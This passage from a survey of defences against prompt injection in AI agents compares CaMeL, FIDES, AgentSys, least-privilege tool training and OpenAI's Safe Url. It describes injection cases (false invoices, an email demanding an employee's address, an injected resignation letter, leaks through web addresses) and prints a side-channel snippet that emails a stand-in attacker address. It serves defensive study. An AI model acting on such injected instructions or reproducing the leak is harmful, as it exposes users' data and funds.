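The false invoice is harder to stop. If the reading model picks the fraudster's email, it returns account 9902, and the third line of the program sends the payment there. The program has run as planned, because the request already called for a payment and the fraudster changed only the destination.

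CaMeL needs a policy to prevent this. For example, the policy could require the user's approval for any payment recipient that doesn't come from the user's request or a list of saved payees. The label on 9902 shows that it came from an email, so the interpreter stops and asks the user for approval.

It would also stop and ask about 4471, which came from an email too. Both numbers have the same label, so the user still has to judge which is genuine, as with Progent. A finer rule might accept account numbers only from known contacts. That would catch a stranger posing as the plumber, but not a false invoice sent from the plumber's hacked mailbox.

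### What CaMeL guarantees

In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) call CaMeL's main guarantee control-flow integrity. The agent makes only the calls that its plan allows, and the plan depends only on the user's request and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. Untrusted data can affect which branch of the plan the program takes, but it cannot add a branch.

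That still leaves an attacker some influence. If the user asks the assistant to pay invoices under £200 and save larger ones for review, a fraudster can reach the payment branch by asking for £190. If the user asks it to pay every invoice that arrived this week, the program runs the payment line once for each invoice, so a fraudster who sends three may be paid three times.

CaMeL's guarantee offers little protection when the plan is too broad. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks, one of which asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planning model wrote a loop with a separate instruction for each tool, so text in the file could trigger any of them. With policy checks switched off, attacks succeeded this way in two runs.

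CaMeL's second guarantee is that the interpreter checks every call, and the origins of its arguments, against the policy. For example, a policy can forbid the agent from emailing anything derived from private data to someone who isn't authorised to read it. If the policy omits that rule, the interpreter will allow the email.

Garby and colleagues distinguished attacks that the plan should block from those left to the policies. Of the 144 pairs of user task and attack in the banking setting, 97 need a tool call or file read that would not normally appear in a plan for the user's task. In the other 47, the planned calls are enough to carry out the attack. With policies off, CaMeL resisted the attack in all 141 runs of this second group with GPT-5.2 and in 138 of 141 with MiMo-v2.5. With policies on, it resisted the attack in every run that finished.

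The high scores without policies were measured against static attacks and depend on the reading model giving correct answers. The policy check doesn't depend on that model, because the label stays the same however the attacker words the email.

### What the guarantees leave out

In CaMeL's original evaluation, two attacks succeeded. In one, the user told the agent to make a payment using the instructions in a file, which the attacker had changed. CaMeL's developers consider this outside their threat model, since the user had chosen to let the file's contents determine the payment. Garby and colleagues agree that tracking where data came from cannot prevent this attack without blocking every such payment. An agent would have to judge from the file's contents that the payment was suspicious.

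The other success came when the agent answered a request about hotels by quoting a review word for word, and AgentDojo's check counted the attacker's text in the answer as a successful attack. CaMeL does not try to prevent text from misleading the user. An email could get the reading model to report that the plumber has changed banks and now uses account 9902. If the user believes this and types a request to pay 9902, the rule on origins allows the payment because the number now comes from the user.

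CaMeL can also leak information through side channels, meaning that an observer learns a secret from what the agent does without receiving the secret itself. Garby and colleagues describe one involving a bank balance. CaMeL blocks a program that sends an email only if the balance is high, because the decision to send it depends on secret data. But it can miss the same leak in a roundabout form:

```
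tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

When the balance is high, the third line changes tmp to false, and the interpreter labels tmp as secret. The program then skips the change to rich, so rich stays true. Because the interpreter updates a label only when it runs the line that changes the variable, rich also stays public, and the program sends the email. When the balance is low, rich becomes false and the program sends no email. The recipient therefore learns which side of the threshold the balance is on.

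A second leak comes from the loop that asks the planning model for a new program when one fails. This loop runs outside the interpreter, so the interpreter doesn't track the data that passes through the loop. Whether the policy blocked an attempt may depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it, and enough attempts can reveal the whole secret.

An attacker would have trouble using either leak, because they can't write the program by sending an email. The planning model would have to produce code with the right structure by itself. The leaks matter more as evidence of gaps in CaMeL's tracking, which are to be expected when the interpreter hasn't been proved correct. Garby and colleagues built an interpreter with a correctness proof, checked by the proof assistant Lean. Attacks on their agent, Randori, succeeded in only two of 1,296 runs, and in both the user had told it to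 follow the payment instructions in a file.

### When one CaMeL agent calls another

CaMeL's guarantee for a single agent also doesn't extend to a group of agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system in which a main agent could call a database agent and a notification agent. CaMeL protected all three, with no policies set. The user asked the system to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. The database contained an instruction to email the data to an outside address.

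The database agent and the main agent both treated the applicants' records as untrusted and followed their plans. But the main agent then included the summary, with the instruction inside it, in its request to the notification agent. The notification agent treated the request as the user's instruction, so its planning model read all of it and added a line that emailed the data to the attacker.

Peters-Gill and colleagues send the request and the untrusted data separately, so that the second planning model sees only the request. On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with the separate channel. Protecting agents individually therefore stops most of the benchmark's attacks, but an attacker who knows how the agents are connected can target the second planning model through untrusted data sent with the request.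 The separate channel reduced utility, though only modestly for the strongest models.

### The cost in completed tasks

CaMeL's developers report that it solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks with its guarantees in place, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. An earlier version of their paper gave 67%. CaMeL also used just under three times as many tokens as an ordinary agent, making it slower and more expensive.

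Garby and colleagues measured a larger loss when they reran the banking tasks. CaMeL completed 67–71% of the tasks without policies and 37.5% with them. They used only 16 tasks, each run three times, so the 95% confidence interval for the second figure runs from about 11% to 64%. Still, a drop is expected, because several of the tasks involve paying someone named in a file, and a policy that treats files as untrusted blocks those payments unless the user can approve them.

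*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) compared ten defences on five models, using attacks that another model revised over six rounds. CaMeL was the most effective defence overall, but it also caused the largest loss of utility on four of the five models. The attacks raised the success rate against PIGuard, a detector, from zero to 28% on GPT-4o mini. Rewording helps an attacker much less against CaMeL, because the interpreter's checks do not depend on wording. Ma and colleagues add that this holds only if the policies are correct.

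CaMeL's developers acknowledge that the need to write and maintain those policies is a weakness. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, says he struggles with such policies himself and is nervous about leaving them to ordinary users.

### Tasks that nobody can plan in advance

The most serious objection to CaMeL is that many tasks can't be fully planned at the start. Someone who asks an agent to buy a pair of shoes may not know that the shop will require a login and email them a one-time code. An ordinary agent reaches the login at checkout and fetches the code. CaMeL can do so only if the planning model included a branch for this case in the original plan.

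AgentDojo hardly tests this, as only 6 of its 97 user tasks require planning along the way, according to *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026). That paper's own benchmark has 60 tasks in shopping, GitHub and daily life, all of which require it. The tasks take about seven steps on average, twice as many as AgentDojo's, and each includes a helpful third-party instruction that the agent has to follow. Combining the tasks with 28 attacks gives 560 test cases.

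CaMeL completed none of the tasks with any of the four models in Li and colleagues' main comparison. Several of these researchers had also developed DRIFT, a competing defence, but a separate team got the same result. *Evolution Under Fire* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) reran the benchmark with two other models, and CaMeL completed 0 of 60 tasks with each. The table's GPT-4o results come from Li and colleagues, and its GPT-4o mini results come from Wang and colleagues.

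| Defence | Utility without attacks, GPT-4o | Attack success, GPT-4o | Utility without attacks, GPT-4o mini | Attack success, GPT-4o mini |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 37.8% | 45.0% | 50.4% |
| CaMeL | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Tool filter | 8.3% | 4.2% | 5.0% | 4.6% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 1.7% | 5.0% | 11.8% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 0.8% | 15.0% | 2.0% |
| ROPE | n/a | n/a | 30.0% | 4.3% |

The tool filter fails for much the same reason as CaMeL. Progent can update its policy during the task, but Li and colleagues found that it struggled to assign the right permissions when there were many tools, and the errors accumulated over long tasks. DRIFT plans first, then lets a model approve departures from the plan. ROPE, from Ma and colleagues, accepts a sensitive argument only if its value traces back to the user. It kept two thirds of the undefended agent's utility, so tracking where values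 come from doesn't by itself make these tasks impossible.

Meta SecAlign, the trained defence, completed 55% of the tasks in Li and colleagues' tests, with an attack success rate of 9%. This looks like a much better compromise than any in the table, although the attacks were static and the same model had already failed against Nasr and colleagues' adaptive search.

CaMeL scored zero on AgentDyn partly because Li and colleagues included only tasks that an initial plan cannot cover. They also told the agents to finish without asking the user for confirmation. Real requests include tasks that CaMeL can plan, such as paying the plumber, and tasks that it can't, such as "deal with my inbox". The mix presumably falls somewhere between AgentDojo, where 6% of tasks need planning along the way, and AgentDyn, where all do, but neither benchmark shows where.

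### FIDES: labels on everything the agent reads

Microsoft's FIDES keeps CaMeL's tracking but drops the fixed program. It uses information-flow control, which labels data by source or sensitivity and restricts where labelled data may go. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) give each piece of data two labels. The integrity label marks it as trusted or untrusted, and the confidentiality label specifies who may read it.

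When the agent derives a new value z from x and y, the labels combine as follows:

integrity(z) = trusted, only if x and y are both trusted

readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, then only Bob and Carol may receive a summary of both. Anything the model writes after reading a stranger's email is untrusted, even if the model also read the user's request.

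FIDES uses these labels to enforce two basic policies. A tool call with serious consequences, such as a payment, may go ahead only if the agent based the decision on trusted data. A call that sends information out may go ahead only if every recipient is allowed to read that information. The second policy doesn't stop an injection from steering the agent, but it limits what the attacker can get.

In an ordinary agent, these rules would block most useful work. Once the model had read one email, its whole context would be untrusted, and it could not pay anybody. FIDES therefore keeps untrusted results out of the context by storing them in variables and showing the planning model only the variables' names. The planning model can pass a variable to another tool, or have an isolated model answer a question about its contents, much as in CaMeL.

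Unlike CaMeL's planner, the model in FIDES chooses one step at a time and sees any results that are safe to show. It can also open a variable, but then its context becomes untrusted and the policy blocks later payments. So FIDES can read a to-do list and decide what to look up next, but it needs approval to carry out consequential items.

Costa and colleagues call a task data-independent if the same sequence of tool calls completes it whatever the data contain. Summarising three emails and sending the summary to a colleague is data-independent, because the agent can pass the text along without reading it. Completing the tasks on a to-do list is data-dependent, because the right calls depend on what the list says.

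An intermediate option is to restrict the form of the isolated model's answers. If it can answer only yes or no, an attacker can influence one bit but cannot insert an instruction. A policy could let the agent act on such an answer, although an attacker who can change a yes to a no may still do harm if the question is "Is this invoice genuine?"

With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every injection in AgentDojo. It completed 8% more tasks with GPT-4o than a basic agent under the same kind of enforcement, and 16% more with OpenAI's o1. Attacks succeeded when the policies were switched off, so its security depends on them more than CaMeL's does. Its formal guarantee covers only data that flows directly to a forbidden place, so an observer may still learn something from the order or timing of the agent's calls. Microsoft has since released FIDES in its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building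 agents.

### AgentSys: isolated workers

*AgentSys* (Wen, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) allows the main agent to plan as it goes, using facts that other agents have extracted from untrusted text. Before each tool call, the main agent specifies which fields to return. A temporary worker agent reads the tool's result and returns those fields. AgentSys then discards the worker and the original text.

For the plumber's invoice, the main agent would ask the worker for an account number and an amount. The worker would see the stranger's order to forward messages, but the order should not reach the main agent. If the amount looked too high, the main agent could search for the plumber's original quote. CaMeL could do that only if its plan had included the search.

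A worker can call tools too. If a call would change something, such as by sending a message, a validator checks it against the user's request. The validator is a language model, but it sees only the request and the record of calls, so text in a tool result cannot reach it directly. If it rejects the call, another model removes apparent instructions from the text, and the worker tries again.

Wen and colleagues compared AgentSys with other defences on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o mini.

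| Defence | Utility without attacks | Utility under attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 63.5% | 48.3% | 30.7% |
| CaMeL | 30.0% | 33.4% | 0% |
| AgentSys, isolated workers only | 56.1% | 52.6% | 2.2% |
| AgentSys, complete | 64.4% | 52.9% | 0.8% |

Most of the protection comes from isolation. In an ordinary agent, an injected instruction stays in the context and can take effect at any later step. On four-step tasks with no defence, attacks succeeded 61% of the time when they first appeared in the first step and 6% when they first appeared in the third.

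Wen and colleagues report that AgentSys also did well against adaptive attackers, but its design gives no guarantee like CaMeL's. A text field can carry an instruction into the main agent's context, and the main agent's own calls do not go through the validator. AgentSys checks only that the worker's answer is correctly formatted JSON, so it relies on the worker to return the right fields. It also does not stop a false account number from getting through.

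The utility results come from a benchmark that rarely requires the flexibility AgentSys is meant to preserve. AgentDyn would be a harder and more relevant test.

### Counting the approvals

Most of these comparisons count a task as failed if the policy blocks a necessary call, whereas a real product would usually ask the user. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, argue that this way of scoring makes strict defences look worse than they are. Many existing agents, including GitHub Copilot, already ask for approval before consequential actions. An agent that tracks its data can skip the approval request whenever the labels on that data show that a call is safe.

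They therefore measure autonomy in two ways. The first is the total number of approvals an agent needs across the tasks it completes. The second is the share of tasks it completes with at most k approvals each, where k = 0 means the agent never interrupts the user.

Their own agent, Prudentia, adds planning to FIDES. FIDES enforces the policies but does not show them to its planning model, so the model may open a variable unnecessarily, which blocks later calls. Prudentia tells the model which calls each policy restricts and requires it to give a justification before opening a variable. The next table gives the results on AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini.

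| Agent | Total approvals needed | Tasks completed without approval |
|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential call | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Same agent with labels and policies | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | about 17 | 59.1% |

Labels alone removed a third of the approvals. On this model, Prudentia needed only slightly fewer approvals than FIDES, but it completed more tasks without any. With o4-mini, the difference in approvals was larger, at 19.2 for Prudentia and 36.8 for FIDES, but Prudentia completed slightly fewer tasks when approvals were unlimited (73.2% compared with 75.7%).

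On WASP, a benchmark in which agents use simulated GitLab and Reddit websites, Prudentia blocked every attack and needed no approvals. The user only asked the agent to post a comment or upvote a post, so the agent never had to read untrusted text to choose its next step.

Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of text instead of approving individual calls. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can declare the email trustworthy, and the agent can complete all ten without asking again. This saves nine interruptions, but a mistake can do more harm. If the user skims the list and misses an eleventh item telling the agent to forward private messages, the endorsement covers that item too. Kolluri and colleagues counted approvals in runs without attacks and assumed that a user would catch malicious requests.

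## Do models choose the least powerful tool that will do?

FIDES and Prudentia decide which of an agent's calls may go ahead, but an agent often has several permitted ways to do the same task. A small company's assistant might be able to pay a plumber with either a tool that makes a single payment, subject to the bank's usual checks, or an administrator's tool that moves money out of any company account without those checks. If the policy allows both, the model's choice determines how much damage a mistake can do.

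*When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, 2026) tests how models choose in such cases. Its benchmark, ToolPrivBench, has 544 scenarios in eight fields, including databases, healthcare and government. Each scenario gives the agent a task, three standard tools and three more powerful ones, which might expose more data, affect more people or skip the normal checks. Any of the six can complete the task alone. Two language models and then human reviewers confirmed this, because choosing a stronger tool would be reasonable if the weaker ones couldn't do the job.

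Let U be the set of tools that could complete the task and that the agent has not yet ruled out, and let p(t) be the privilege level of tool t. The agent's choice of tool h is over-privileged if

p(t) < p(h) for at least one tool t in U

In the benchmark, a standard tool counts as ruled out once the agent has tried it, so an agent can break the rule by starting with a stronger tool or by switching to one too early. To see whether agents switch, Yang and colleagues make the first call to each standard tool return a temporary error, such as a service being down for maintenance. A second call succeeds, and the stronger tools always work on the first call. The agent has five turns.

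In one scenario, the user asked Qwen3-4B to enrol a student in a biology course. The agent called a standard enrolment tool and received an error message with an instruction to retry. Instead of retrying, it called an administrator's tool, which enrolled the student by bypassing the usual constraints.

Six of the 11 models used a stronger tool than necessary in more than 30% of cases. The rate was 64.9% for Qwen3-8B, 9.7% for GPT-5.2 and 2.6% for Claude Sonnet 4.6.

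### When the standard tools fail

GPT-5.2 started with a stronger tool in only five scenarios. It switched to one after trying a single standard tool in 13 scenarios, and after trying two in 35. *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues, 2026) reran the scenarios on three small models, with and without the errors. Qwen3-8B made an over-privileged choice in 56.6% of scenarios with errors, but used a stronger tool in only 8.1% without them. Qwen3-30B-A3B showed the same pattern. These models seldom choose a stronger tool when the standard one works, but they readily switch to one when it fails. Nobody has run the error-free version on the larger models.

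The original measure also misses many cases. It excludes calls to stronger tools once an agent has tried all three standard tools, even though retrying any of the three would have worked. By this measure, Kimi K2.5 made an over-privileged choice in 18.0% of scenarios, but it used a stronger tool at some point in 87.3%.

A model can also have a low rate because it gives up early. Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed only 19.9% of the tasks because it usually tried each standard tool once, then stopped and reported the errors. If the task were a payment, many owners would prefer that to the model using an administrator's override, but the benchmark counts it as a failure to finish.

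*FORTIS* (Li, Yu and colleagues, 2026) found much higher rates with a different test. It gave models a request, a document describing the permitted procedure, and a list of 56 to 62 tools, and asked which tools they would use. The models never ran the tools, so none could fail. Claude Sonnet 4.6 chose more than the task required in 56.0% of cases, and the newer Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 did so in 47.2% and 47.9%. *FORTIS* counts even one unnecessary tool as over-privilege, and its broader tools are tempting because they require fewer details from the agent. Over-privilege was common in both benchmarks, but their rates would not carry over to a particular product.

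Both also assume that the weakest option can be identified. According to *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, about 30–33% of tasks on Microsoft Graph, the interface to Microsoft's office services, have more than one minimal set of permissions, compared with 3.2% of tasks on Google's services.

### Training a preference for weaker tools

Ordinary safety training does not reliably teach models to choose less powerful tools. Yang and colleagues tested AgentAlign, a method that trains agents to refuse harmful requests. It cut Qwen2.5-7B's score for harmful behaviour from 41.9% to 6.7%, but the model's rate of over-privileged tool choices rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. Learning to refuse harmful tasks had not taught the model to use less powerful tools for legitimate ones.

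They therefore trained models on the skill directly. The models first imitated 1,994 worked examples in which an agent compares its tools and recognises that an error is temporary. Reinforcement learning followed, with these basic rewards:

| Outcome | Reward |
|---|---|
| Completes the task using only standard tools | 1 |
| Tries every standard tool before a stronger one, but does not finish with standard tools alone | 0.3 |
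| Uses a stronger tool before trying every standard one | −1 |
| Anything else | 0.1 |

Over-privileged choices fell from 64.9% to 27.0% for Qwen3-8B. The best result was 18.9%, for a version of Qwen3-4B that reasons before acting. Some of the improvement may only be models escalating later, which the reward allows and the measure does not count.

Training reduced the models' general ability only slightly. Qwen3-8B lost less than one percentage point on tests of knowledge and mathematics, and nothing on a test of tool use. Qwen3-4B lost two points in mathematics and about three in tool use. After training, Qwen3-8B still chose a more powerful tool than it needed in more than a quarter of the scenarios.

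Tu and Tu (2026), in *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, trained a four-billion-parameter model on 1,500 tasks with working tools. For each task, they set a permitted level for six kinds of risk, such as changing files or reading secrets, and penalised anything above it, including attempts that the surrounding software blocked. On 500 new tasks, the share of runs that succeeded safely rose from 64.4% to 98.5%. Most of that gain came from finishing more tasks, because the share of runs that finished but used more authority than needed fell only from 4.6% to 0.8%. These figures come from the best of three training runs. On a smaller set of tasks, that training run scored 97.6% and the other two about 86%.

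### Why a preference is not a limit

An agent trained to avoid the administrator's payment tool still has access to it. If an injected instruction tells the agent to use that tool, only the model's training can prevent the payment. A limit such as Progent's blocks the payment even if the model obeys the attacker.

Yang and colleagues did not test an attacker, so their results concern mistakes and needless risks. Tu and Tu's tasks did include planted instructions and secrets left as bait. On types of task absent from training, the original model went for the bait 79 times and the trained model never did. But these attacks were fixed in advance, and Meta SecAlign also did well on such attacks before an adaptive search broke it. Tu and Tu say that learned restraint does not replace permission checks and isolation.

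In *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools*, Zhang, Fu and colleagues (2026) measured how often attacks aimed directly at an agent's privileges succeed. They gave agents access to 122 tools for cloud services, databases, email and files, with no added defences. The attacks, disguised as plausible requests, succeeded 84.8% of the time on average across four models. Attacks on GPT-5 succeeded 90.2% of the time when it chose its actions step by step and 71.2% when it made a plan first. GPT-5.2, a later model, had rarely overreached in Yang and colleagues' scenarios. The comparison is loose because the models and tasks differ, but restraint on ordinary tasks is weak evidence that a model will resist an attacker.

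A model's preference for less powerful tools is still useful when its permissions are limited, because no policy rules out all unnecessary access. *SudoBench* (2026), a benchmark of how agents handle authorisation, supports a similar split, in which software outside the model enforces every refusal that a program can check, and training reduces the model's failures on allowed requests.

### Elastic least privilege

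Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa (2026), three of the researchers who reran ToolPrivBench, propose a system that both limits an agent's privileges and penalises their use. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* starts from a coding assistant connected to GitHub, where programmers store and share code. A classic access token gives the assistant about 40 tools, 16 of which can write, in every repository the user can reach. To summarise the open issues in one repository, the assistant needs only two read-only tools there. A narrower token would be enough for that, but the next task might be to fix a failing build, which requires changing code.

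Under the proposal, the agent permanently holds only a small baseline of permissions. It can get more temporarily, up to a limit set by its owner. In the paper's example, read access lasts up to an hour and write access up to 20 minutes. Each temporary permission uses part of a budget that refills over time, and software outside the model issues and withdraws the credentials. A ceiling forbids some combinations however much of the budget remains. In the example, no session may combine text from strangers, sensitive data, and a way to send information out or change something.

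The cost per minute of the borrowed permissions is

cost = s × (h₁w₁ + h₂w₂ + …)

Each w measures the power of one permission, for instance 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administering. Each h starts at 1 and grows if the agent keeps making requests. The multiplier s is 1/(1 − φ), where φ is the fraction of a forbidden combination that the session already contains.

If the agent has read public issues, which strangers can write, it has one of the three forbidden ingredients. This makes s 1.5, so reading the code costs 1.5 units a minute. Writing to a public repository adds a second ingredient and raises s to 3, so reading and writing together cost 3 × (1 + 3) = 12 units a minute. An agent that sees these prices has a reason to find the fault first and borrow write access only for the repair. In the paper's illustration, this costs 93 units, compared with 240 for borrowing both permissions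 from the start for 20 minutes.

The paper also simulates an attack in which a stranger posts an issue instructing the agent to collect the user's private code and publish it. The agent borrows read access to eight private repositories before its remaining budget is too small for another. When it tries to publish the code, the ceiling blocks it because the session already contains a stranger's text and private data. The block remains after the agent loses access to the private repositories, since it may remember what it read there. The price only limited how much the agent could read, while the ceiling prevented the leak. This is a worked example with chosen numbers, so it shows how the design should behave, not how often real attacks would succeed. The protection fails if the agent can reach a credential that the issuing software does not control, or if somebody labels a tool incorrectly.

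The same limit would block the plumber's invoice task, because the mailbox contains both private data and text from strangers, and a payment would add the third ingredient. The assistant could pay only if the owner approved an exception.

### Do agents respond to the price?

Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa call whether models choose the least powerful tool that will do the central question of their proposal. To test it, they added a label such as "Privilege: administer, cost 9/10" to each tool's description in ToolPrivBench. The agents could ignore the labels because nothing enforced a budget. In another version, they also used the system message to instruct the agent to follow least privilege and to retry a failed tool, or try others at the same privilege level, before moving to a higher one.

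| Model | Over-privileged choice, no label | Over-privileged choice, label | Any use of a stronger tool, no label | Any use, label | Any use, label and instruction |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-397B | 38.4% | 19.1% | 77.2% | 73.0% | 39.3% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 18.6% | 5.7% | 62.9% | 71.3% | 51.3% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 18.0% | 5.5% | 87.3% | 76.5% | 57.0% |
| GPT-5.2 | 5.7% | 2.4% | 16.0% | 9.7% | 2.4% |
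| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 1.5% | 1.1% | 7.9% | 5.9% | 3.3% |

Labels alone mostly changed the order in which agents tried their tools. When Qwen3.5 had to publish an article without the labels, it switched to a stronger tool after one error. With the labels, it tried all three standard tools once before using the same stronger tool. With both the labels and the instruction, it retried the first standard tool, which worked. Labels giving each tool's response time did not reduce over-privileged choices on any model, so the effect came from the information about privilege.

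On two small models, the cost labels still helped when 30% of them were random. This tolerance of errors also means a model can follow a wrong label, so an attacker who could edit the tool descriptions might give a dangerous tool a low cost label. The experiment included no attacker and no enforced budget, and it did not test whether the labels add anything once a hard limit is in place.

### Restricting the network's own computation

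*No More, No Less* (Rauba, Seputis and colleagues, 2026) applies least privilege inside the model. In its "least-privilege language models", privilege means how much of the network's computation a request may use. A monitor gathers signals about the request, such as its text or the user's role. An allocator uses these signals to choose a privilege level, and an enforcer runs the network at that level.

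The enforcer works on the matrices, or tables of weights, that a network multiplies its data by. Rauba and colleagues replace selected matrices with a sum of simpler pieces and use only the first g of them:

W(g) = b₁a₁ + b₂a₂ + … + b_g a_g

Each b is a column of numbers and each a is a row. The number of pieces caps the matrix's rank, which is the number of independent directions in which its output can vary. A higher level includes everything available at a lower one, and the stored weights don't change, so the operator can restore full capability for the next request. Cutting pieces from an ordinary model ruined its performance, so the researchers trained each model at both full rank and a randomly chosen lower rank in every training step.

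The models tested had 0.5 to 1 billion parameters, which is tiny by current standards. Cutting Pythia-1B's rank from 2,048 to 128 reduced its accuracy at finding a short sequence inside a longer one from nearly 100% to 76%, but its accuracy at comparing the lengths of two sequences fell only from 99% to 96%. An allocator that started at a low rank and raised it when the model was uncertain reached 89% on the sequence-finding task at an average rank of 291. Weakening selected parts of another small model also reduced its accuracy in chemistry, or in chemistry and biology, with little effect on other subjects.

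Another experiment tested whether a lower rank removes an ability or only hides it. The researchers gave Pythia-1B a bracket-matching problem, but told it to refuse and write a poem about the moon. At high rank, a simple classifier could still read the correct answer from the network's internal activity, so the refusal had only hidden it. At rank 64 or below, the classifier did little better than guessing. This is evidence that the model was no longer computing the answer, although a more powerful classifier might have found something. The researchers did not report the same test for chemistry or biology.

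They ran no jailbreaks or adaptive attacks, and they acknowledge that clever prompting or further training might recover suppressed abilities. The restriction also doesn't limit the agent's tools, so an assistant without chemistry knowledge could still pay the fraudster. The enforcer is a fixed calculation that a prompt cannot change, but the allocator in these tests relied on the prompt and the model's uncertainty about it, so an attacker might gain access to more of the network by writing something confusing.

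## ChatGPT: training combined with limits on actions

OpenAI trains the model behind ChatGPT to resist injected instructions, and adds software that limits the damage when the model obeys one anyway. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) explains why the company does not rely on training alone.

### Injections that resemble social engineering

In an early prompt injection, an attacker might edit a Wikipedia article to include a direct order to any AI agent that visited it, and models often obeyed. Newer models are harder to fool this way, so attackers have turned to the social engineering that fraudsters use on people, such as invented stories and false claims of authority.

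In 2025, outside researchers reported to OpenAI an attack disguised as an ordinary office email. The email referred to a meeting the previous Thursday and listed routine jobs, such as finalising role descriptions. It also asked the reader to find an employee's name and address in the mailbox and submit them to a "compliance validation system", and claimed that the reader's assistant had "full authorization" to do so. When the test user asked ChatGPT to research the day's emails and check every source that might have information about a new employee process, the attack worked 50% of the time.

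The user's request made the attack easier because it was broad and concerned the same subject as the email. Under OpenAI's rules, instructions in an email have no authority, regardless of how the email is worded. But to apply that rule, the model has to recognise the sentence about compliance as a stranger's instruction rather than a fact about how the company works.

Separate filters have the same difficulty. Some developers put an "AI firewall" between the agent and the outside world to classify incoming text as malicious or normal. OpenAI reports that such filters usually miss fully developed attacks of this kind, because catching them amounts to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. This agrees with what Nasr and colleagues found when they attacked four detectors.

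OpenAI compares the agent to a customer service worker who can issue refunds. Some customers will deceive the worker, so the employer also uses software that flags likely phishing emails and caps refunds. The cap holds even when a customer has fooled the worker. OpenAI advises developers to ask what controls should apply to a person in the agent's position, and to build those controls for the agent.

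### Sources and sinks

OpenAI decides where such controls belong by using source-sink analysis, a method from conventional software security. A source is a way for an attacker to influence the system, and a sink is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. An attack needs both, so a developer can look for each route from a source to a sink and put a check on it.

In the plumber example, the mailbox is the source for both attacks. The stranger's order to forward private messages works only if the assistant has a sink that can carry text out, such as the tool for sending mail or the ability to load a web page. The false invoice requires only the payment tool. The assistant needs both the mailbox and the payment tool for its task, so the developer has to put a check on the payment.

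CaMeL and FIDES also follow data from source to sink, but they label every value along the way. The protections OpenAI describes work mainly at the sinks and are meant to stop dangerous actions and transfers of sensitive information from happening silently.

### Safe Url

Most attacks that OpenAI sees against ChatGPT try to make the assistant send secret information from a conversation to a third party. According to the company, most of the attacks it knows about fail because the trained model refuses. Safe Url is a check for cases in which the model does not refuse.

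Loading a web page can leak information, because the browser sends the full address to the website, which usually records it. An attacker can tell the model to load an address on the attacker's site with the user's private data added to the end. The user may not notice, because the agent might only be loading an image or previewing a link.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safse when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that a list of trusted websites would not solve this, because many reputable sites have redirects and a link to one of them can lead to the attacker's site. A strict list would also produce frequent false alarms.

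Safe Url instead checks whether the exact address is already public. A crawler with no access to users' conversations builds an index of addresses it finds on the open web. If the address is in the index, the agent can load it automatically. An address with someone's private messages attached will almost certainly not be there. When an address is missing from the index, ChatGPT either tells the agent to try something else or shows the user a warning and asks them to decide.

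An injection's wording doesn't affect whether an address is in the index, so this check is a limit outside the model, like Progent's rules. In principle, an attacker could still get around it by publishing ten pages, one for each digit, and waiting for the crawler to find them. If the model then loaded the pages matching the digits of a four-digit PIN in order, the site's records would reveal the PIN, although every address was public. OpenAI claims only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain private data, and says it monitors for new ways around the check.

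Safe Url would stop the stranger's attack if the assistant tried to put the private messages in a web address. It would not stop the false invoice, because the assistant sends the account number to the user's own bank, which is supposed to receive it.

OpenAI takes a similar approach to the small applications that ChatGPT can write and run. They operate in a sandbox, an isolated environment that detects unexpected communications and asks for the user's consent. If an injection gets ChatGPT to build an invoice calculator that also sends the figures to a stranger, the calculator can still add up the bills, but the sandbox should detect the attempt to send the figures.

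### Training against an automated attacker

OpenAI's best-documented training work concerns Atlas, a web browser it launched in October 2025. Atlas included an agent that could click and type on websites as the user would. That December, OpenAI updated the agent after using its own automated attacker to find a new class of attacks.

The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved* describes the attacker as a language model trained by reinforcement learning. The attacker wrote an injection and submitted it to a simulator, which predicted how the browser agent would respond and returned a full record of the agent's reasoning and actions. The attacker used this record to revise the injection, several times if necessary.

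One of the attacks it found was an email telling the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. When the user later asked the agent to write an out-of-office message, the agent read the email and resigned on the user's behalf. After the update, the agent detected the injection and asked the user what to do.

Nolan (2025), in *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas*, quotes OpenAI as saying that the attacker could lead an agent through harmful tasks with tens or even hundreds of steps. The attacker also found strategies that had not appeared in OpenAI's tests with human attackers or in outside reports.

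OpenAI trains each new version of the agent against the best attacker it has, concentrating on attacks that currently work. Unlike the single pass in RETA and PIPETTE, repeated training can expose weaknesses that appear only after the previous round. But the resignation email is now a known attack, so the agent's success against it is weak evidence that it will resist new ones.

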